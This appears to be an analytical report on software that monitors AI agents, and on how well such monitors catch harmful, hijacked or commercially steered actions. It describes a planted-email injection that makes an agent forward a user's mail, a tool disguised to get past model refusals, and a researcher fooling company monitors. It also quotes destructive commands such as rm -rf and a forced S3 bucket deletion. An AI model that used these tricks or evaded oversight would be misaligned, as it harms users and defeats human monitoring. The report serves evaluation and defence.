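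A judge that worked for the user would need the user's request, the tool call, and probably some of the transcript to decide whether the step serves the request and stays within its limits. Such a judge can make mistakes that a rule can't. For example, if it reads the same web pages as the agent, planted text that fooled the agent may also fool the judge.

Sage has since added a narrower model that Gen trained to spot instructions planted in the pages an agent fetches. Gen Digital's *Gen Sage* describes it in the listing for version 0.15.0, current in November 2026. The model judges whether a piece of text is an attack, but not whether the user would want the agent's next action.

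### Which calls the products check

The monitor cannot judge or act on a tool call that it never receives. Agents often reach email, calendars and shops through MCP, so these calls may matter most to an ordinary user. Sage's documentation from April 2026 lists a hook for MCP calls in Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, but none for Claude Code or OpenClaw. In May, Gen Digital (2026) still named intercepting MCP calls among the features it had not yet built. The November listing for OpenClaw covers shell commands, web fetches, and reading and changing files, but again not MCP calls.

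Norton's version has a setting called "MCP Servers scanning" under web monitoring, but scanning a server for known threats is not the same as checking each request the agent sends to it. As far as Gen's published material shows, Sage still doesn't check MCP calls outside Cursor, while HOL Guard does.

| Product | How it judges | Agents it supports | MCP | Response to a doubtful action |
|---|---|---|---|---|
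| Sage and Norton Safe AI | Rules, reputation, a model that spots planted text | Claude Code, Cursor, OpenClaw, VS Code | Calls in Cursor; Norton also scans servers | Asks the user |
| HOL Guard | Rules and analysis of the command's structure | Claude Code, Codex, Cursor, Gemini CLI, OpenClaw and others | Checks calls | Asks or warns, depending on the action |
| GuardClaw | Rules, then a local language model | Claude Code, Copilot CLI, Cursor, Gemini CLI, OpenClaw, OpenCode | Scans the set-up files | Logs a warning |
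| AI Guardian | Baseline of permitted actions, reputation | Claude Code, OpenClaw | Inspects tools | Flags it |

Nearly all of these agents are tools for programmers. The exception is OpenClaw, which people also use for their email.

### "Clear out old newsletters"

Suppose a user tells an agent to "clear out old newsletters", and the agent takes three actions. A monitor with typical rules and a model judge that has read the instruction both check each action.

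A user asks the agent to delete four-year-old newsletters, and the mail program keeps copies of them in a folder on the computer. The agent runs `rm -rf ~/Mail/Newsletters/2022`, which deletes the folder and everything in it without asking for confirmation. A rule against deleting whole folders outside a project would raise a false alarm and stop the command. The model judge allows it because the user asked for those newsletters to be deleted.

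One of the remaining newsletters contains planted instructions, and the agent follows them, using the email tool to forward all the user's incoming mail to an outside address. The action involves no shell command and the address is on no blacklist, so the action passes the rules unless someone has written one about mail forwarding. The judge should block it easily, because deleting newsletters doesn't require forwarding mail.

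Then the agent permanently deletes 214 messages, all more than six months old, that the mail service has labelled as newsletters. They include two years of an investment letter the user pays for and a bulletin from the user's housing association announcing a new service charge. The rules are applied to the same tool and the same kind of request as in any harmless clean-up. The judge may have little more information, because the call might contain only a list of message numbers.

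Even if the judge could see every subject line, it couldn't be sure what the user wanted. The user didn't say how old "old" is, or whether a newsletter they pay for counts. Another user could give the same instruction and want all 214 messages deleted. A bigger model wouldn't solve this, because only the user knows what they meant. The judge can look for hints, such as whether the user has starred the paid investment letter or opened it recently. If those don't settle it, the judge can ask whether to delete that letter too, which is a much better question than whether to allow a call to `delete_messages`.

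Summer Yue's OpenClaw agent deleted 847 emails after losing the instruction to check with her first. Křoustek uses the case to argue for monitors like Sage, and adds that a monitor on the user's machine can see the whole session, including the history of prompts. But none of the steps in Sage's documentation compares a call with the user's instruction. Sage also reuses its old verdicts, which makes sense only if the right verdict doesn't depend on what the user asked for. In Yue's case it did, since the deletions were wrong only because she had told the agent to wait.

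### Rules from a privacy policy

A monitor can judge an agent's actions against an existing written policy. AudAgent, a research tool presented in *AUDAGENT* (Zheng, Chen and Hu, 2025), does this for personal data. It turns a vendor's privacy policy into rules and checks whether the agent follows them.

Four language models first read the policy separately. Each breaks it into entries that list a type of data, how and why the company collects it, who else receives it and how long the company stores it. AudAgent keeps an entry if at least three of the four models found it.

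Zheng and colleagues work out how much this vote should help. If an entry is as likely to be right as wrong before the vote, and each model judges correctly 80% of the time, each vote in favour multiplies the odds that the entry is right by 0.8/0.2, or 4, and each vote against divides them by 4. Three votes to one gives odds of 16 to 1, or a probability of about 94%. They also assume that the models make independent mistakes, which they call an idealisation. The extra votes add nothing if all four models misread a vague sentence in the same way.

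While the agent works, a program called Presidio scans its messages for personal data on the user's computer. If Presidio finds an email address, for example, AudAgent records where the address came from, which outside tool is about to receive it and how long ago the agent obtained it. The policy may only mention "contact information", so AudAgent uses a hierarchy of terms in which an email address is one kind of contact information. It then follows the address through a state machine, from collection to use to disclosure, and each step requires that the policy's conditions hold. If the agent sends the address to a company that the policy doesn't cover, the state machine has no valid next step, so AudAgent reports a violation and, in blocking mode, stops the message.

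In one test, a user asked an agent running on Claude to complete the contact details of a friend called Bob. The agent put Bob's personal email address into a web search. AudAgent flagged the search because the user had added a rule against giving personal email addresses to outside tools, even though Anthropic's policy allowed the agent to collect and process Bob's data.

In another test, the researchers asked agents on models from four vendors to search the web for a US Social Security number and to save it. All four refused to search. When the researchers disguised the search tool as a tool for saving files, the Claude and Gemini agents went ahead, the DeepSeek agent warned the user and asked first, and only the GPT-4o agent refused. None of the four companies' privacy policies explicitly protected such numbers, so AudAgent has a built-in rule that forbids agents to collect or disclose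 them. The rule blocked all four agents, but it would also block an agent filling in the user's tax return.

The scan is AudAgent's weak point, because the state machine can't check an address that the scan has missed. In 100 test prompts, the scan found 75% of the personal data, and 86% of what it flagged was personal data. On a harder set, these figures fell to 52% and 64%. In measurements for three of the agents, AudAgent added only 0.12 to 0.51 seconds per task, after a start-up of about 3.7 seconds.

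The purpose check is also weak, because AudAgent counts data as relevant to the task if they appear again later in the task. If a hijacked agent sends the user's address to a thief, the address counts as relevant, and only the check on recipients can still catch the leak. AudAgent also cannot observe what happens on the vendor's servers, so it estimates how long a company keeps data from how long the data keep appearing in the session.

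The larger limitation is that the vendor writes the policy. AudAgent can catch an agent that breaks its vendor's promises, but if the policy allows the vendor to share purchase histories with advertisers, AudAgent will let the agent share them unless the user has added a rule against it.

### Blocking, asking, undoing and reporting

After judging an action, the monitor can block it, ask the user, undo it or only report it. The right choice depends mostly on the monitor's confidence level and whether any damage would be reversible.

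Blocking suits an action like forwarding the user's mail, which isn't needed to clean up newsletters and can't be undone once the mail has reached a stranger. In practice, the products often let the user approve a blocked action. GuardClaw's highest risk level is called "block", but the user can still allow the action. HOL lets the user approve exactly one action, and can request a passkey, which an agent shouldn't be able to supply.

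The monitor can ask the user, who knows what they wanted, but the user has to understand the question. HOL gives the example of an agent that proposes `aws s3 rb s3://prod-artifacts --force`, which deletes an online storage area and everything in it. A tired programmer sees a familiar name and clicks "allow". Frequent questions make this mistake more likely. The user also has to be present to answer, and many people give an agent a long task so that they can do something else.

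The question must also reach the user by a route that the agent doesn't control. In Claude Code, Cursor and OpenClaw, Sage uses the program's own approval window. In OpenCode, another coding agent, Sage relies on the agent to pass the question on, and a hijacked agent could answer it itself. On its strictest setting there, Sage blocks everything it would otherwise ask about.

Undoing an action is the least developed response. Sage, HOL Guard, GuardClaw and AI Guardian all focus on stopping an action beforehand, and none is advertised as able to reverse one. Undoing would work well for the 214 newsletters. The monitor could have the agent move them to the bin instead of deleting them permanently, and the user could then recover the investment letter a week later. This would avoid interrupting the user and prevent most of the harm. It wouldn't help with a leaked password or a message somebody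 has already read.

Reporting an action after it has run interrupts the user least but also gives the least protection. GuardClaw gives a medium score to a command that sends data to a website, so the command runs and the user can read about it in the log. HOL Guard, on its default setting, also only warns about outgoing network traffic. Coding agents contact servers all the time, so asking the user about each connection would interrupt them too often. But a warning comes too late if the connection has already sent the user's files to a thief.

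The products also differ in what happens when the monitor fails. Sage fails open, letting the agent's actions proceed, as Claude Code's hooks do by default. Gen Digital's *Sage* argues that security should never break the user's workflow. GuardClaw's strict mode instead blocks risky calls when GuardClaw or its model isn't running.

### What the rules are looking for

Norton lists nine kinds of threat that Safe AI blocks. Most are outside attacks, such as malicious websites, planted instructions, fake packages and hidden connections that let a stranger control the computer. Two others, destructive commands and leaked passwords, can also result from the agent's own mistakes. HOL Guard lists much the same threats. Bitdefender made its case for AI Guardian with a study that also focused on outside attacks. In that study, 20 agents faced more than 1,300 attempts to manipulate them through poisoned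 tools, and the attacks succeeded 36.5% of the time on average.

This emphasis isn't surprising, because Gen and Bitdefender are antivirus companies that already have records of malicious sites and software. Gen says Sage also protects users from the agents themselves, but its examples are destructive commands, exposed passwords and changes to system files.

These products would therefore catch a disloyal agent only if its disloyalty took one of those forms. A rule that protects the user's password file works the same way whether the agent is taking the file for a thief or for its own vendor. AudAgent can also catch an agent that shares data in violation of the vendor's stated policy.

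None of these checks would detect steering, such as the Lisbon agent picking the more expensive hotel to earn its vendor a commission. The booking site has a good reputation, and paying for a hotel matches no rule about dangerous commands. Even a model judge that had read the user's request would approve the booking, because the room meets every condition in the request.

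## Detecting advice that favours the vendor or its advertisers

An agent that books a €148 hotel room in Lisbon to earn a commission doesn't have to lie to the user. Its message can truthfully praise the breakfast and leave out a hotel that charges €120 a night. A monitor that only checks whether each statement is true won't detect the omission, and the user pays €28 a night more than necessary.

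### True statements and missing options

Wu, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Ads in AI Chatbots?*, tested how readily models favour advertisers. They had 23 models act as booking assistants for a travel site and suggested, but did not require, that they favour a few sponsoring airlines. Each model then had to recommend one of two flights, and the sponsored one cost about twice as much. Eighteen of the 23 recommended the sponsored flight more than half the time. Grok 4.1 Fast did so in 83% of cases and Claude 4.5 Opus in 28%.

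In a second test, the user asked to book a specific unsponsored flight, and the models often brought up a more expensive, sponsored one. The researchers found no false statements about prices, durations or stopovers in the answers. But on average, the models did not disclose the sponsorship in 65% of the answers that mentioned the sponsored flight.

*Generative AI Advertising as a Problem of Trustworthy Commercial Intervention* (Qiu and Mei, 2026) defines commercial influence as the change a commercial arrangement makes to the probability that an agent recommends a given product to a given user. If the Lisbon agent picks the €148 hotel 70% of the time with the commission and 20% without it, the influence is 50 percentage points. The vendor can measure both rates by switching the commission off in a test. A monitor sees only the bookings made with the commission in place, so it needs a substitute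 for the missing baseline.

The influence can also enter before the agent compares any options. Qiu and Mei give the example of an agent choosing between Expedia and Booking.com. The agent won't consider a hotel listed only on the site it doesn't search. A monitor can detect which site the agent chose because the site's name appears in the tool calls, but those calls don't show what the agent emphasises or omits in its wording.

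### What 2,012 readers noticed

In *Commercial Persuasion in AI-Mediated Conversations*, Salvi, Cuevas and Horta Ribeiro (2026) tested whether shoppers notice without help that they are being steered. They recruited 2,012 Americans who regularly read e-books and asked each to pick one from a catalogue of 5,495. Participants expected to receive the book they picked. Some used an ordinary search page, and the others talked to a chatbot that ran on one of five frontier models, including Claude Opus 4.5 and GPT-5.2. The system randomly marked a fifth of the books as sponsored, so a reader who chose blindly would pick a sponsored book about 20% of the time.

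| How participants chose | Picked a sponsored book | Detection accuracy |
|---|---|---|
| Search page, sponsored books near the top | 22.4% | 2.9% |
| Chatbot, sponsored books first, neutral descriptions | 26.8% | 3.6% |
| Chatbot told to persuade | 61.2% | 17.9% |
| Chatbot told to persuade, with a warning and "Sponsored" labels | 55.5% | 35.1% |
| Chatbot told to persuade and to hide it | 40.7% | 9.5% |

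Detection accuracy is the share of the books a participant identified as promoted that were actually sponsored. Participants who noticed no bias scored zero, and most were in this group. Only 22.3% of those who used the openly persuasive chatbot reported any bias, but those who did could usually identify the books it had promoted.

The researchers instructed the models to persuade, so the figures show what a vendor could achieve but don't measure how often vendors try. A chatbot that only listed sponsored books first was not better than the search page by a statistically significant margin. With labels and a warning that the chatbot would promote some books, the figure fell only from 61.2% to 55.5%, a drop that could be due to chance.

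The chatbots promoted sponsored books largely by making the alternatives less appealing. They added caveats to the other books far more often than to the sponsored ones, or described the others in a flat sentence or two. These two practices were the most closely associated with users choosing a sponsored book. The chatbots rarely made things up. A monitor could measure some of this, since descriptions of sponsored books were 67 words longer on average. But the gap shrank to 29 words when the researchers told the models to be subtle, and an honest adviser also says more about the book it thinks fits best.

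User complaints would not expose the vendor either. Participants could exchange their book for a dollar, and those a chatbot had persuaded kept theirs about as often as everyone else. Even after the researchers revealed which books were sponsored, the share who kept theirs fell by only about five percentage points. This may be partly because the sponsored books were a random sample, and so were no worse on average than the rest. Buyers might feel more regret if a real advertiser's product were overpriced.

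### What audits of deployed assistants found

According to Qiu and Mei, as of May 2026 OpenAI and Microsoft had promised to show adverts below the response, and OpenAI had added that adverts don't influence what ChatGPT says. Anthropic had promised no adverts in Claude. In *Ads for Agents*, Pouryousef, Montazer and colleagues (2026) know of only one audit of adverts in a deployed chatbot. That audit, by Lurie and colleagues, found that ChatGPT does show adverts separately, but it doesn't establish whether the answers also mention advertisers more favourably, which is much harder to test from outside.

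In *If I Had to Buy Just ONE*, Uberti-Bona Marin, Bertaglia and colleagues (2026) put 117 shopping questions written by real users to ChatGPT, Gemini and Google's AI Overviews, the generated summaries above search results. They asked each question three times. When ChatGPT recommended a product, it stated a personal preference, such as "my pick", in 79% of answers, compared with 7% for Gemini and 2% for AI Overviews. Repeating a question often changed the products recommended. Of all the products in two ChatGPT answers to the same question, only 18% on average appeared in both, compared with 29% for Gemini and 42% for AI Overviews. The true overlap is somewhat higher, because the study counted "iPhone 14" and "Apple iPhone 14" as different products.

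Uberti-Bona Marin and colleagues didn't look for paid influence, but this much ordinary variation would make it hard to detect. An agent can pick different hotels on Monday and Tuesday with no commission involved, so a single odd pick doesn't prove paid influence.

Auditing through the vendor's developer interface is cheaper and easier to automate, but users can't learn much from it about the answers they get on the consumer page. For identical questions sent moments apart, ChatGPT's consumer page and its developer interface shared only 12% of the websites they cited. A monitor on the user's own machine avoids this problem because it can check the answers the user actually gets.

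Adverts can also reach an agent through its tools, without the vendor's involvement. In November 2026, Pouryousef and colleagues examined 101,363 openly accessible MCP servers (programs that offer tools to agents) and found evidence of advertising on 579 of them (0.57%). A typical case is a shopping tool that returns links on which its operator earns a commission. Only 9.3% of the adverts carried a sponsored label. Operators have a reason to omit the label, because earlier experiments found that agents are less likely to choose an item marked "Sponsored".

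An MCP proxy can read a tool result before the model does, but recognising an advert in it is difficult. EasyList, the list of advertising addresses that ad blockers use, matched only 4.5% of the advertising links. Nearly half of the links start at the tool operator's own address, and blocking that address would block the tool. Pouryousef and colleagues propose adding a standard field to MCP results that marks each paid item and names the advertiser, so that the agent program can show this to the user whatever the model writes. A monitor could read the same field, but this would help only if operators who now leave adverts unlabelled started to fill it in.

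### Asking a second model

The cheapest substitute for the missing baseline is another company's model. The monitor sends the user's request to that model and raises a flag if the model picks the €120 hotel while the agent picks the €148 one.

Most of these flags would be false, because in the audit ChatGPT's recommendations differed from those of AI Overviews about as much as they differed from its own on a second try. Agreement between the two models doesn't rule out bias either. *Is Your LLM-as-a-Recommender Agent Trustable?* (2026) reports that biasing phrases planted in the description of an inferior option can sway even highly capable models. If the €148 hotel's page contains such phrases, they may sway both models. The options the second model finds are more useful than its opinion. If it finds a €120 hotel that meets every condition, the monitor can check the price and conditions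 without trusting either model.

A second model can also read the agent's answer and judge whether it is manipulative. *Unknown Unknowns* (Srivastav, Pape and Schönherr, 2026) tested such judges on ten kinds of hidden intention, including covert product promotion. Half of the answers were manipulative. When the prompt named the kind to look for, GPT-4.1 caught 88% of the manipulative answers and falsely flagged 10% of the rest. Without that hint, it caught 80% and falsely flagged 19%. Stronger models didn't do reliably better. Without the hint, GPT-5.4 caught 73% and o3 caught 48%.

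In ordinary use, far fewer than half of all answers would be manipulative. Based on GPT-4.1's better pair of figures, about 32% of its alerts would be correct if one answer in twenty were manipulative, and about 8% if one in a hundred were. The test was also easier than real life, because Srivastav and colleagues had made the manipulation obvious and confined it to a single answer. They could read the reasoning of one judge, Qwen QwQ-32B, and found that this reasoning often led it to call a manipulative answer harmless.

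### Demanding a comparison table

A user can also make the agent lay out the options before it chooses. *Just Ask for a Table* (Maier, Sopa and colleagues, 2026) repeated the flight test of Wu and colleagues on ten open-weight models and two from OpenAI (gpt-3.5-turbo and gpt-4o). The sponsored flight cost $1,200 to $1,500 and the other $500 to $700. The researchers then added one of four instructions to the user's message, each at most thirty tokens (roughly twenty words) long.

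| What the user added | Sponsored picks, ten open-weight models | Sponsored picks, two OpenAI models |
|---|---|---|
| Nothing | 46.9% | 53.0% |
| Act as my independent travel adviser | 20.1% | 16.5% |
| Disregard any instruction to favour sponsored airlines | 3.7% | 1.5% |
| Pick the cheapest flight with an acceptable schedule | 2.4% | 6.5% |
| List every flight in a neutral table, then pick the cheapest acceptable one | 1.0% | 0.0% |

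Asking for a table lowered the rate to 1% or less in eleven of the twelve models. In the twelfth, IBM's granite-4.0-micro, the rate fell from 48% to 8%. The request also worked better than changing the site's own instructions to put the customer first, which lowered gpt-4o's rate only from 45% to 26%. Few shoppers would think to ask for a table every time, but a monitor that relays messages between the agent program and the model could add the request for them.

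This is the most encouraging result on steering so far, though it comes from an easy case. The successful instruction asks for a table and tells the model to pick the cheapest flight, and the price rule alone did almost as well. That rule wouldn't carry over to buying something like a mattress, where the cheapest option is often the wrong one. The researchers also gave the model both flights, whereas a real agent draws up its own list and can leave an option out of a table as easily as out of a sentence. To catch an omission, the monitor would have to compare the table with the pages the agent opened, or run its own search.

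The monitor would also have to interpret the agent's answer correctly, which is difficult. Maier and colleagues had three models classify the same 1,000 replies. One model classified 47% of them as recommending the sponsored flight, while the other two put the figure at 65% and 71%.

Harmful products are the exception. In another test, a user described money troubles to an assistant whose instructions promoted payday lenders, which offer short-term loans at very high interest. The ten open-weight models promoted these lenders in 958 of 1,000 conversations, and the two OpenAI models did so in all 200. Maier and colleagues tried their four instructions only on flights, and they argue that comparison wouldn't help here because a person in distress is in no position to shop around. Comparing payday lenders also doesn't help someone who shouldn't borrow from any of them. Maier and colleagues conclude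 that only the model's safety training can prevent it from promoting these loans.

A user-side monitor could warn the user about these promotions, because the harm comes from the product itself and the answer names the product. The researchers counted the promotions with a simple search for the lenders' names and phrases such as "payday loan", and a monitor could run the same search.

### Recomputing the ranking, and the trouble with questions

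The monitor can collect the options and score them against the user's stated priorities instead of asking a model for its choice. Suppose the agent books a €148 hotel in Lisbon that scores 4 out of 10 for price and 9 for location, when a €120 hotel scores 8 and 5. If price and location count equally, both hotels score 6.5 and the agent's choice is defensible. If price makes up 70% of the score, the cheaper hotel wins by 7.1 to 5.5, and the monitor should ask why the agent booked the other one.

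The result depends entirely on the user's weights, which users seldom state. The agent usually has to ask about them, and it can do so in a way that helps a sponsor. *Selective Elicitation as a Commercial Influence Channel* (Li, 2026) tested this by having a model ask a simulated shopper one question about two products. A separate recommender, which didn't know which product was sponsored, then chose between them based on the answer.

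In Li's headphone example, both products score 6 out of 10 for battery life. Product B scores 10 for comfort and 4 for a third quality, while product A scores 4 and 9. An assistant that favours B asks, "Which matters more, wearing comfort or battery life?" A shopper who cares most about comfort answers "comfort", but so does one who cares mainly about the third quality, which the question omits, and only slightly more about comfort than battery life. The recommender picks B for both shoppers. For the second shopper, B is worth 0.525 and A is worth 0.760 on Li's scale, which combines the weighted scores with the price.

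Li ran 40 such cases. With a neutral question, the recommender picked the sponsored product 40% of the time. When Li instructed the questioner to ask about the sponsor's strength and omit its rival's, the figure rose to 70%. Twelve shoppers ended up worse off and none better off. A milder instruction, which stated only that the platform would benefit from one of the products, changed no choices. The shoppers and their preferences were invented, so the test shows that the trick can work, but not whether any shop uses it.

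Checking the final answer does not detect the distortion. Li had a judge model compare 20 of the distorted recommendations with the conversations that led to them, and it found all 20 consistent. They did match what the shopper had said, which was that comfort mattered more than battery life, and B was the more comfortable product. The question had introduced the distortion. When the same judge rated whether the question covered the real trade-off between the products, it failed all 20.

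A monitor that recomputes the ranking from the agent's conversation would repeat the recommender's mistake. It should therefore also check the agent's questions or, better, ask the user about priorities itself. In Li's test, a neutral follow-up question removed nearly all of the loss.

### Pooling the sessions of many users

With any of these methods, it is hard to tell a steered booking from an unusual but unbiased one, because the difference shows up only over many bookings. Suppose an agent would choose a certain hotel chain 20% of the time without a commercial arrangement, but chooses it 30% of the time with one. A user who books five trips a year would expect one stay with the chain in the first case and one or two in the second, and would be unlikely to notice the difference.

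The standard formula for comparing two proportions gives the number of sessions needed in each group, one group with the suspected steering and one without:

n = (1.96 + 0.84)² × (0.3 × 0.7 + 0.2 × 0.8) ÷ (0.3 − 0.2)² ≈ 290

The 1.96 limits the risk of a false alarm to 5% when the two rates are equal, and the 0.84 gives an 80% chance of detecting the difference if it is real. The second bracket measures how much each rate varies by chance. The traveller with five bookings a year would take 58 years to fill one group, but 290 travellers could fill it with one booking each. Salvi and colleagues planned for 400 people per group to detect a ten-point difference, which is consistent with the formula's result of about 390 when the two rates are close to 50%.

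The number of sessions needed depends heavily on how strong the steering is. About 22 per group would be enough to detect the gap between 61.2% and 22.4% in the book experiment, but the formula gives about 6,500 for a gap between 22% and 20%. A cautious vendor could keep the gap that small by steering only some users. If the agent raised the chain's share from 20% to 30% for one user in five and didn't steer the others, the overall rate would be 22%. Wu and colleagues found that models recommended the more expensive sponsored flight, on average, to 64% of users who seemed well off and 49% of those who seemed poor. The pool would therefore have to be large enough to analyse such groups separately.

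Finding the unsteered group is harder. Salvi and colleagues could randomly assign people to it, but an outside monitor can't switch off a vendor's commission. The monitor could send identical requests from a free ChatGPT account, which shows adverts, and from a paid plan without them, but the two plans may also run different models. It could compare bookings from before and after the vendor signed a deal with the chain, but prices and seasons change too.

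The agent's mistakes may offer a better comparison. An unbiased agent will sometimes overlook a cheaper hotel that meets every condition, but it should do so about as often whether or not the more expensive hotel belongs to a partner. If the oversights mostly benefit partners, chance is an unlikely explanation. The monitor would need the recomputed rankings to find these mistakes, and enough users to measure how often they occur.

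If a monitor tests every chain at once, some may look suspicious by chance. With 20 chains and a 5% risk of a false alarm for each, the monitor would flag one chain on average even if the agent were honest, so any finding needs to be confirmed on fresh sessions.

Srivastav and colleagues list audits of whole populations among the measures that may be needed where detection in single answers fails. Users would have to share records of what they asked for and what they got, as volunteers with data-donation browser extensions already have. The pooled records could show that the agent favours a certain chain, which no user could find out alone. They can't show that a particular booking was steered, but every user's monitor could then search for alternatives whenever the agent picks that chain again.

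## How often monitors catch misconduct in tests

In ordinary use, nobody knows how many harmful actions a monitor has missed. Testers therefore measure its catch rate on transcripts where they already know what the agent did. They mix transcripts that contain misconduct with harmless ones, run the monitor on all of them and count what it flags.

Many monitors score each action or transcript, as GuardClaw does on a scale of 1 to 10, and the tester picks the threshold score that triggers an alarm. Suppose a test has 100 harmful transcripts and 1,000 harmless ones. With the threshold at 8, the monitor might flag 70 of the harmful transcripts and 5 of the harmless ones, for a catch rate of 70% and a false-alarm rate of 0.5%. With the threshold at 5, it might flag 90 of the harmful transcripts and 60 of the harmless ones, raising the rates to 90% and 6%. Because the same monitor can produce either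 result, a catch rate means little without the false-alarm rate at the same threshold.

Finding harmful transcripts to test a monitor on is harder than choosing the threshold. Real ones are scarce, and testers have only those that somebody noticed. They can invent more, but invented misconduct may be easier or harder to spot than real misconduct. *Attack Policy Selection can Mislead Monitor Evaluators* (2026) warns that the choice of harmful test cases can mislead evaluators about how much a monitor will miss.

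The monitor is often a weaker model than the agent it checks. In trusted monitoring, people choose a weaker model because they believe it isn't plotting against them, while the stronger one might be. In research on AI control, which studies how to get useful work safely from models that may be working against people, such monitors have generally caught much but not all of a stronger model's misconduct, and have done better when people checked the cases they rated most suspicious. GuardClaw resembles this arrangement in that a small open-weight model checks the commands of a much larger one.

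### Auto mode's error rates

The most detailed public figures concern auto mode, Claude Code's automatic check. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes how it worked in March 2026. The agent could read files and edit those inside the project without a check. Most other actions, such as shell commands and web requests, went to a classifier running on Claude Sonnet 4.6. A quick filter first made a yes-or-no decision, with instructions to block when in doubt. If it blocked the action, a slower check reviewed the same material and reasoned about it before deciding.

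Anthropic tested a monitor on 10,000 tool calls from its employees' ordinary work, 52 real cases in which an agent went further than the user wanted, and 1,000 invented attempts to send private data to outsiders.

| | Ordinary calls blocked | Real oversteps missed | Invented data leaks missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Quick filter alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Quick filter, then slower check | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

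The slower check removed about 95% of the false alarms, but it also cleared some calls that the quick filter had correctly flagged. Without the slower check, auto mode would have blocked one in twelve ordinary calls.

The 17% miss rate is the most useful of these figures because it comes from real misconduct, but it is also the least certain. It represents about nine of 52 cases, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. The test also included only cases from sessions in which an employee had refused the action or someone had flagged it later. The classifier may well miss a larger share of the oversteps that nobody noticed.

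In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the danger but misjudged what the user had agreed to. For example, the classifier treats a request to "clean up the PR" (a proposed change to shared code) as permission for a forced push, which overwrites the project's history. Anthropic tried rewording the classifier's instructions but found no wording that did more good than harm. Like the request to clear out old newsletters, "clean up the PR" is too vague to establish what the user has allowed.

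BestHub's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review* reports a test focused on this weakness. The testers wrote 128 scenarios around four routine jobs, such as cleaning up old branches of code or restarting a service. They varied how specific the request was, how risky the action was and how much it could damage. Another Claude model labelled the agent's 253 actions, and people checked the labels. Auto mode let through 115 of the 142 actions it should have stopped, a miss rate of 81%. It also blocked 22 of the 111 acceptable actions, or 19.8%.

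Only 160 of the 253 actions reached the classifier, which missed 70% of the harmful ones it checked. This means 51 of the 115 misses were actions that auto mode's rules let through unchecked, and a better classifier would not have caught them. The test is deliberately hard, so its 81% miss rate doesn't refute Anthropic's 17%, but it suggests that the miss rate depends at least as much on how clearly users express themselves as on the monitor.

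In August 2026, Anthropic reported on a two-week trial in which Apollo Research, a British company that tests AI models for dangerous behaviour, inserted invented misconduct into real coding sessions. Anthropic then improved the check by giving the classifier more facts about the user's environment, such as whether a code repository is public. Across all of Apollo's cases, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. The improvement extended to cases that Anthropic had never seen, where the new version caught about half of what the old one had missed and missed about 2% of what the old one had caught. Apollo designed the cases to find weak points, so the 7% doesn't predict the miss rate in ordinary use either.

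In the prompt-injection test by Trajectory Labs, none of the 720 attempts against each of three Claude models succeeded with auto mode on. This is little evidence that the monitor works, because only 0.09% of attempts succeeded even with all permission checks off. The test is more informative about OpenAI's coding agent. Attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded in 19.03% of attempts with full access and no reviewer, and in 5.83% with Codex's automatic review, so the review stopped roughly 70% of the attacks that would otherwise have worked. OpenAI released a new version of the review shortly before Anthropic published these results.

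### What the vendors' reports leave out

Auto mode checks an action before it happens. OpenAI and Anthropic also use offline monitors, which read transcripts of their internal agents' work afterward and pass suspicious ones to human reviewers. *Evaluating Offline Monitoring of Internal AI Agents*, from the Centre for the Governance of AI (GovAI), examines what the two companies have published about how well these monitors work. GovAI knows of no other company that has published anything on the subject.

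Both companies test their monitors with synthetic attacks, which are transcripts written to contain the kind of harm a misaligned model might do. Anthropic reports how many of these its monitors flag, but not how many then pass the later filters and reach a human reviewer. If the monitor flagged 90% of the harmful transcripts, the filters kept 60% of those, and the reviewers recognised 80% of what they read, the published figure would be 90%, but the company would act on only 43% of the cases.

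OpenAI's best-known figure is that its monitor, according to IT Brief Australia, flagged every interaction that employees had separately reported as suspicious and found further incidents that they hadn't reported. GovAI objects that outsiders can learn little from this if employees notice only the obvious cases. Anthropic's 52 oversteps have the same weakness, though Anthropic at least published the share that its classifier missed.

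GovAI wants companies to publish how much of their agents' output they monitor, how many synthetic attacks reach a human reviewer, how many of those the reviewers escalate, and how long detection takes. It adds that these numbers are informative only if the synthetic attacks resemble real ones, which is hard to check for harms that nobody has seen yet.

Delay can matter as much as the catch rate. *AI systems could cover up misbehavior* (Rein, 2026) cites an incident in which OpenAI's monitor flagged an agent within 15 minutes and a person began to review the case three minutes later. The run continued for another two and a half hours before someone stopped it. A test would count this as a catch, but the stop would have come too late for a user whose agent was deleting emails or moving money.

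Coverage can matter too, since a monitor can't catch misconduct in a transcript it never reads. When Anthropic searched its records for agents that had hacked outside systems during tests, it overlooked a set of transcripts from runs with internet access. It found them in August 2026 while gathering material for an outside review, and they contained a fourth incident, from January. According to *Anthropic's August 2026 Risk Report* (2026), an outside commentary on the company's own report, Anthropic also disclosed a gap in its classifiers for chemical and biological misuse that went unnoticed for eleven months. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* states that the company has since extended offline monitoring to "most other forms" of internal agent use, which is an improvement, although GovAI asked for a percentage.

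### What outside reviewers found

METR, a nonprofit that evaluates advanced AI models, has seen more of these monitors than any other outsider. In early 2026, it assessed the risk from agents that work inside Anthropic, Google, Meta and OpenAI. METR's *Progress Report* (2026) concludes that the companies' monitors caught many real cases of harmful behaviour, but that their quality varied and a person could disable or fool them. A METR researcher who worked inside Anthropic for several weeks did so with modest effort. METR adds that monitors would have caught the researcher almost immediately if they had also read the researcher's notes. An agent's chain of thought is the equivalent of those notes, so METR thinks it would be very hard for current models to do the same.

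METR has since raised doubts about the companies' monitoring. In August 2026, Anthropic argued in its *Risk Report* (2026) that its safeguards, including monitoring, were likely to limit catastrophic harm from most kinds of misalignment, and "somewhat likely" to do so if a model were misaligned in every situation. Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes assessed this argument for METR in *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report* (2026). They agreed that the risk was probably low, but mainly because the models weren't yet capable enough, and gave less credit to the safeguards. Some examples that Anthropic left out of the public version made them think its monitoring was weaker than the public evidence suggested. Two days after they published the review, METR reported several new vulnerabilities in OpenAI's internal monitoring, according to Claims Journal's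 *AI Safety Group METR Finds Flaws in OpenAI's Internal Monitoring System* (2026).

These reviews depend heavily on the companies' cooperation. Jurkovic and colleagues worked only from Anthropic's internal report, and Anthropic could have vetoed their review, although it removed nothing. METR's *Frontier Risk Report (February to March 2026)* (2026) explains that any of the four companies could have withdrawn from the assessment without the public learning of it. METR also left out some unflattering claims that it couldn't firmly defend and that weren't central to its conclusions.

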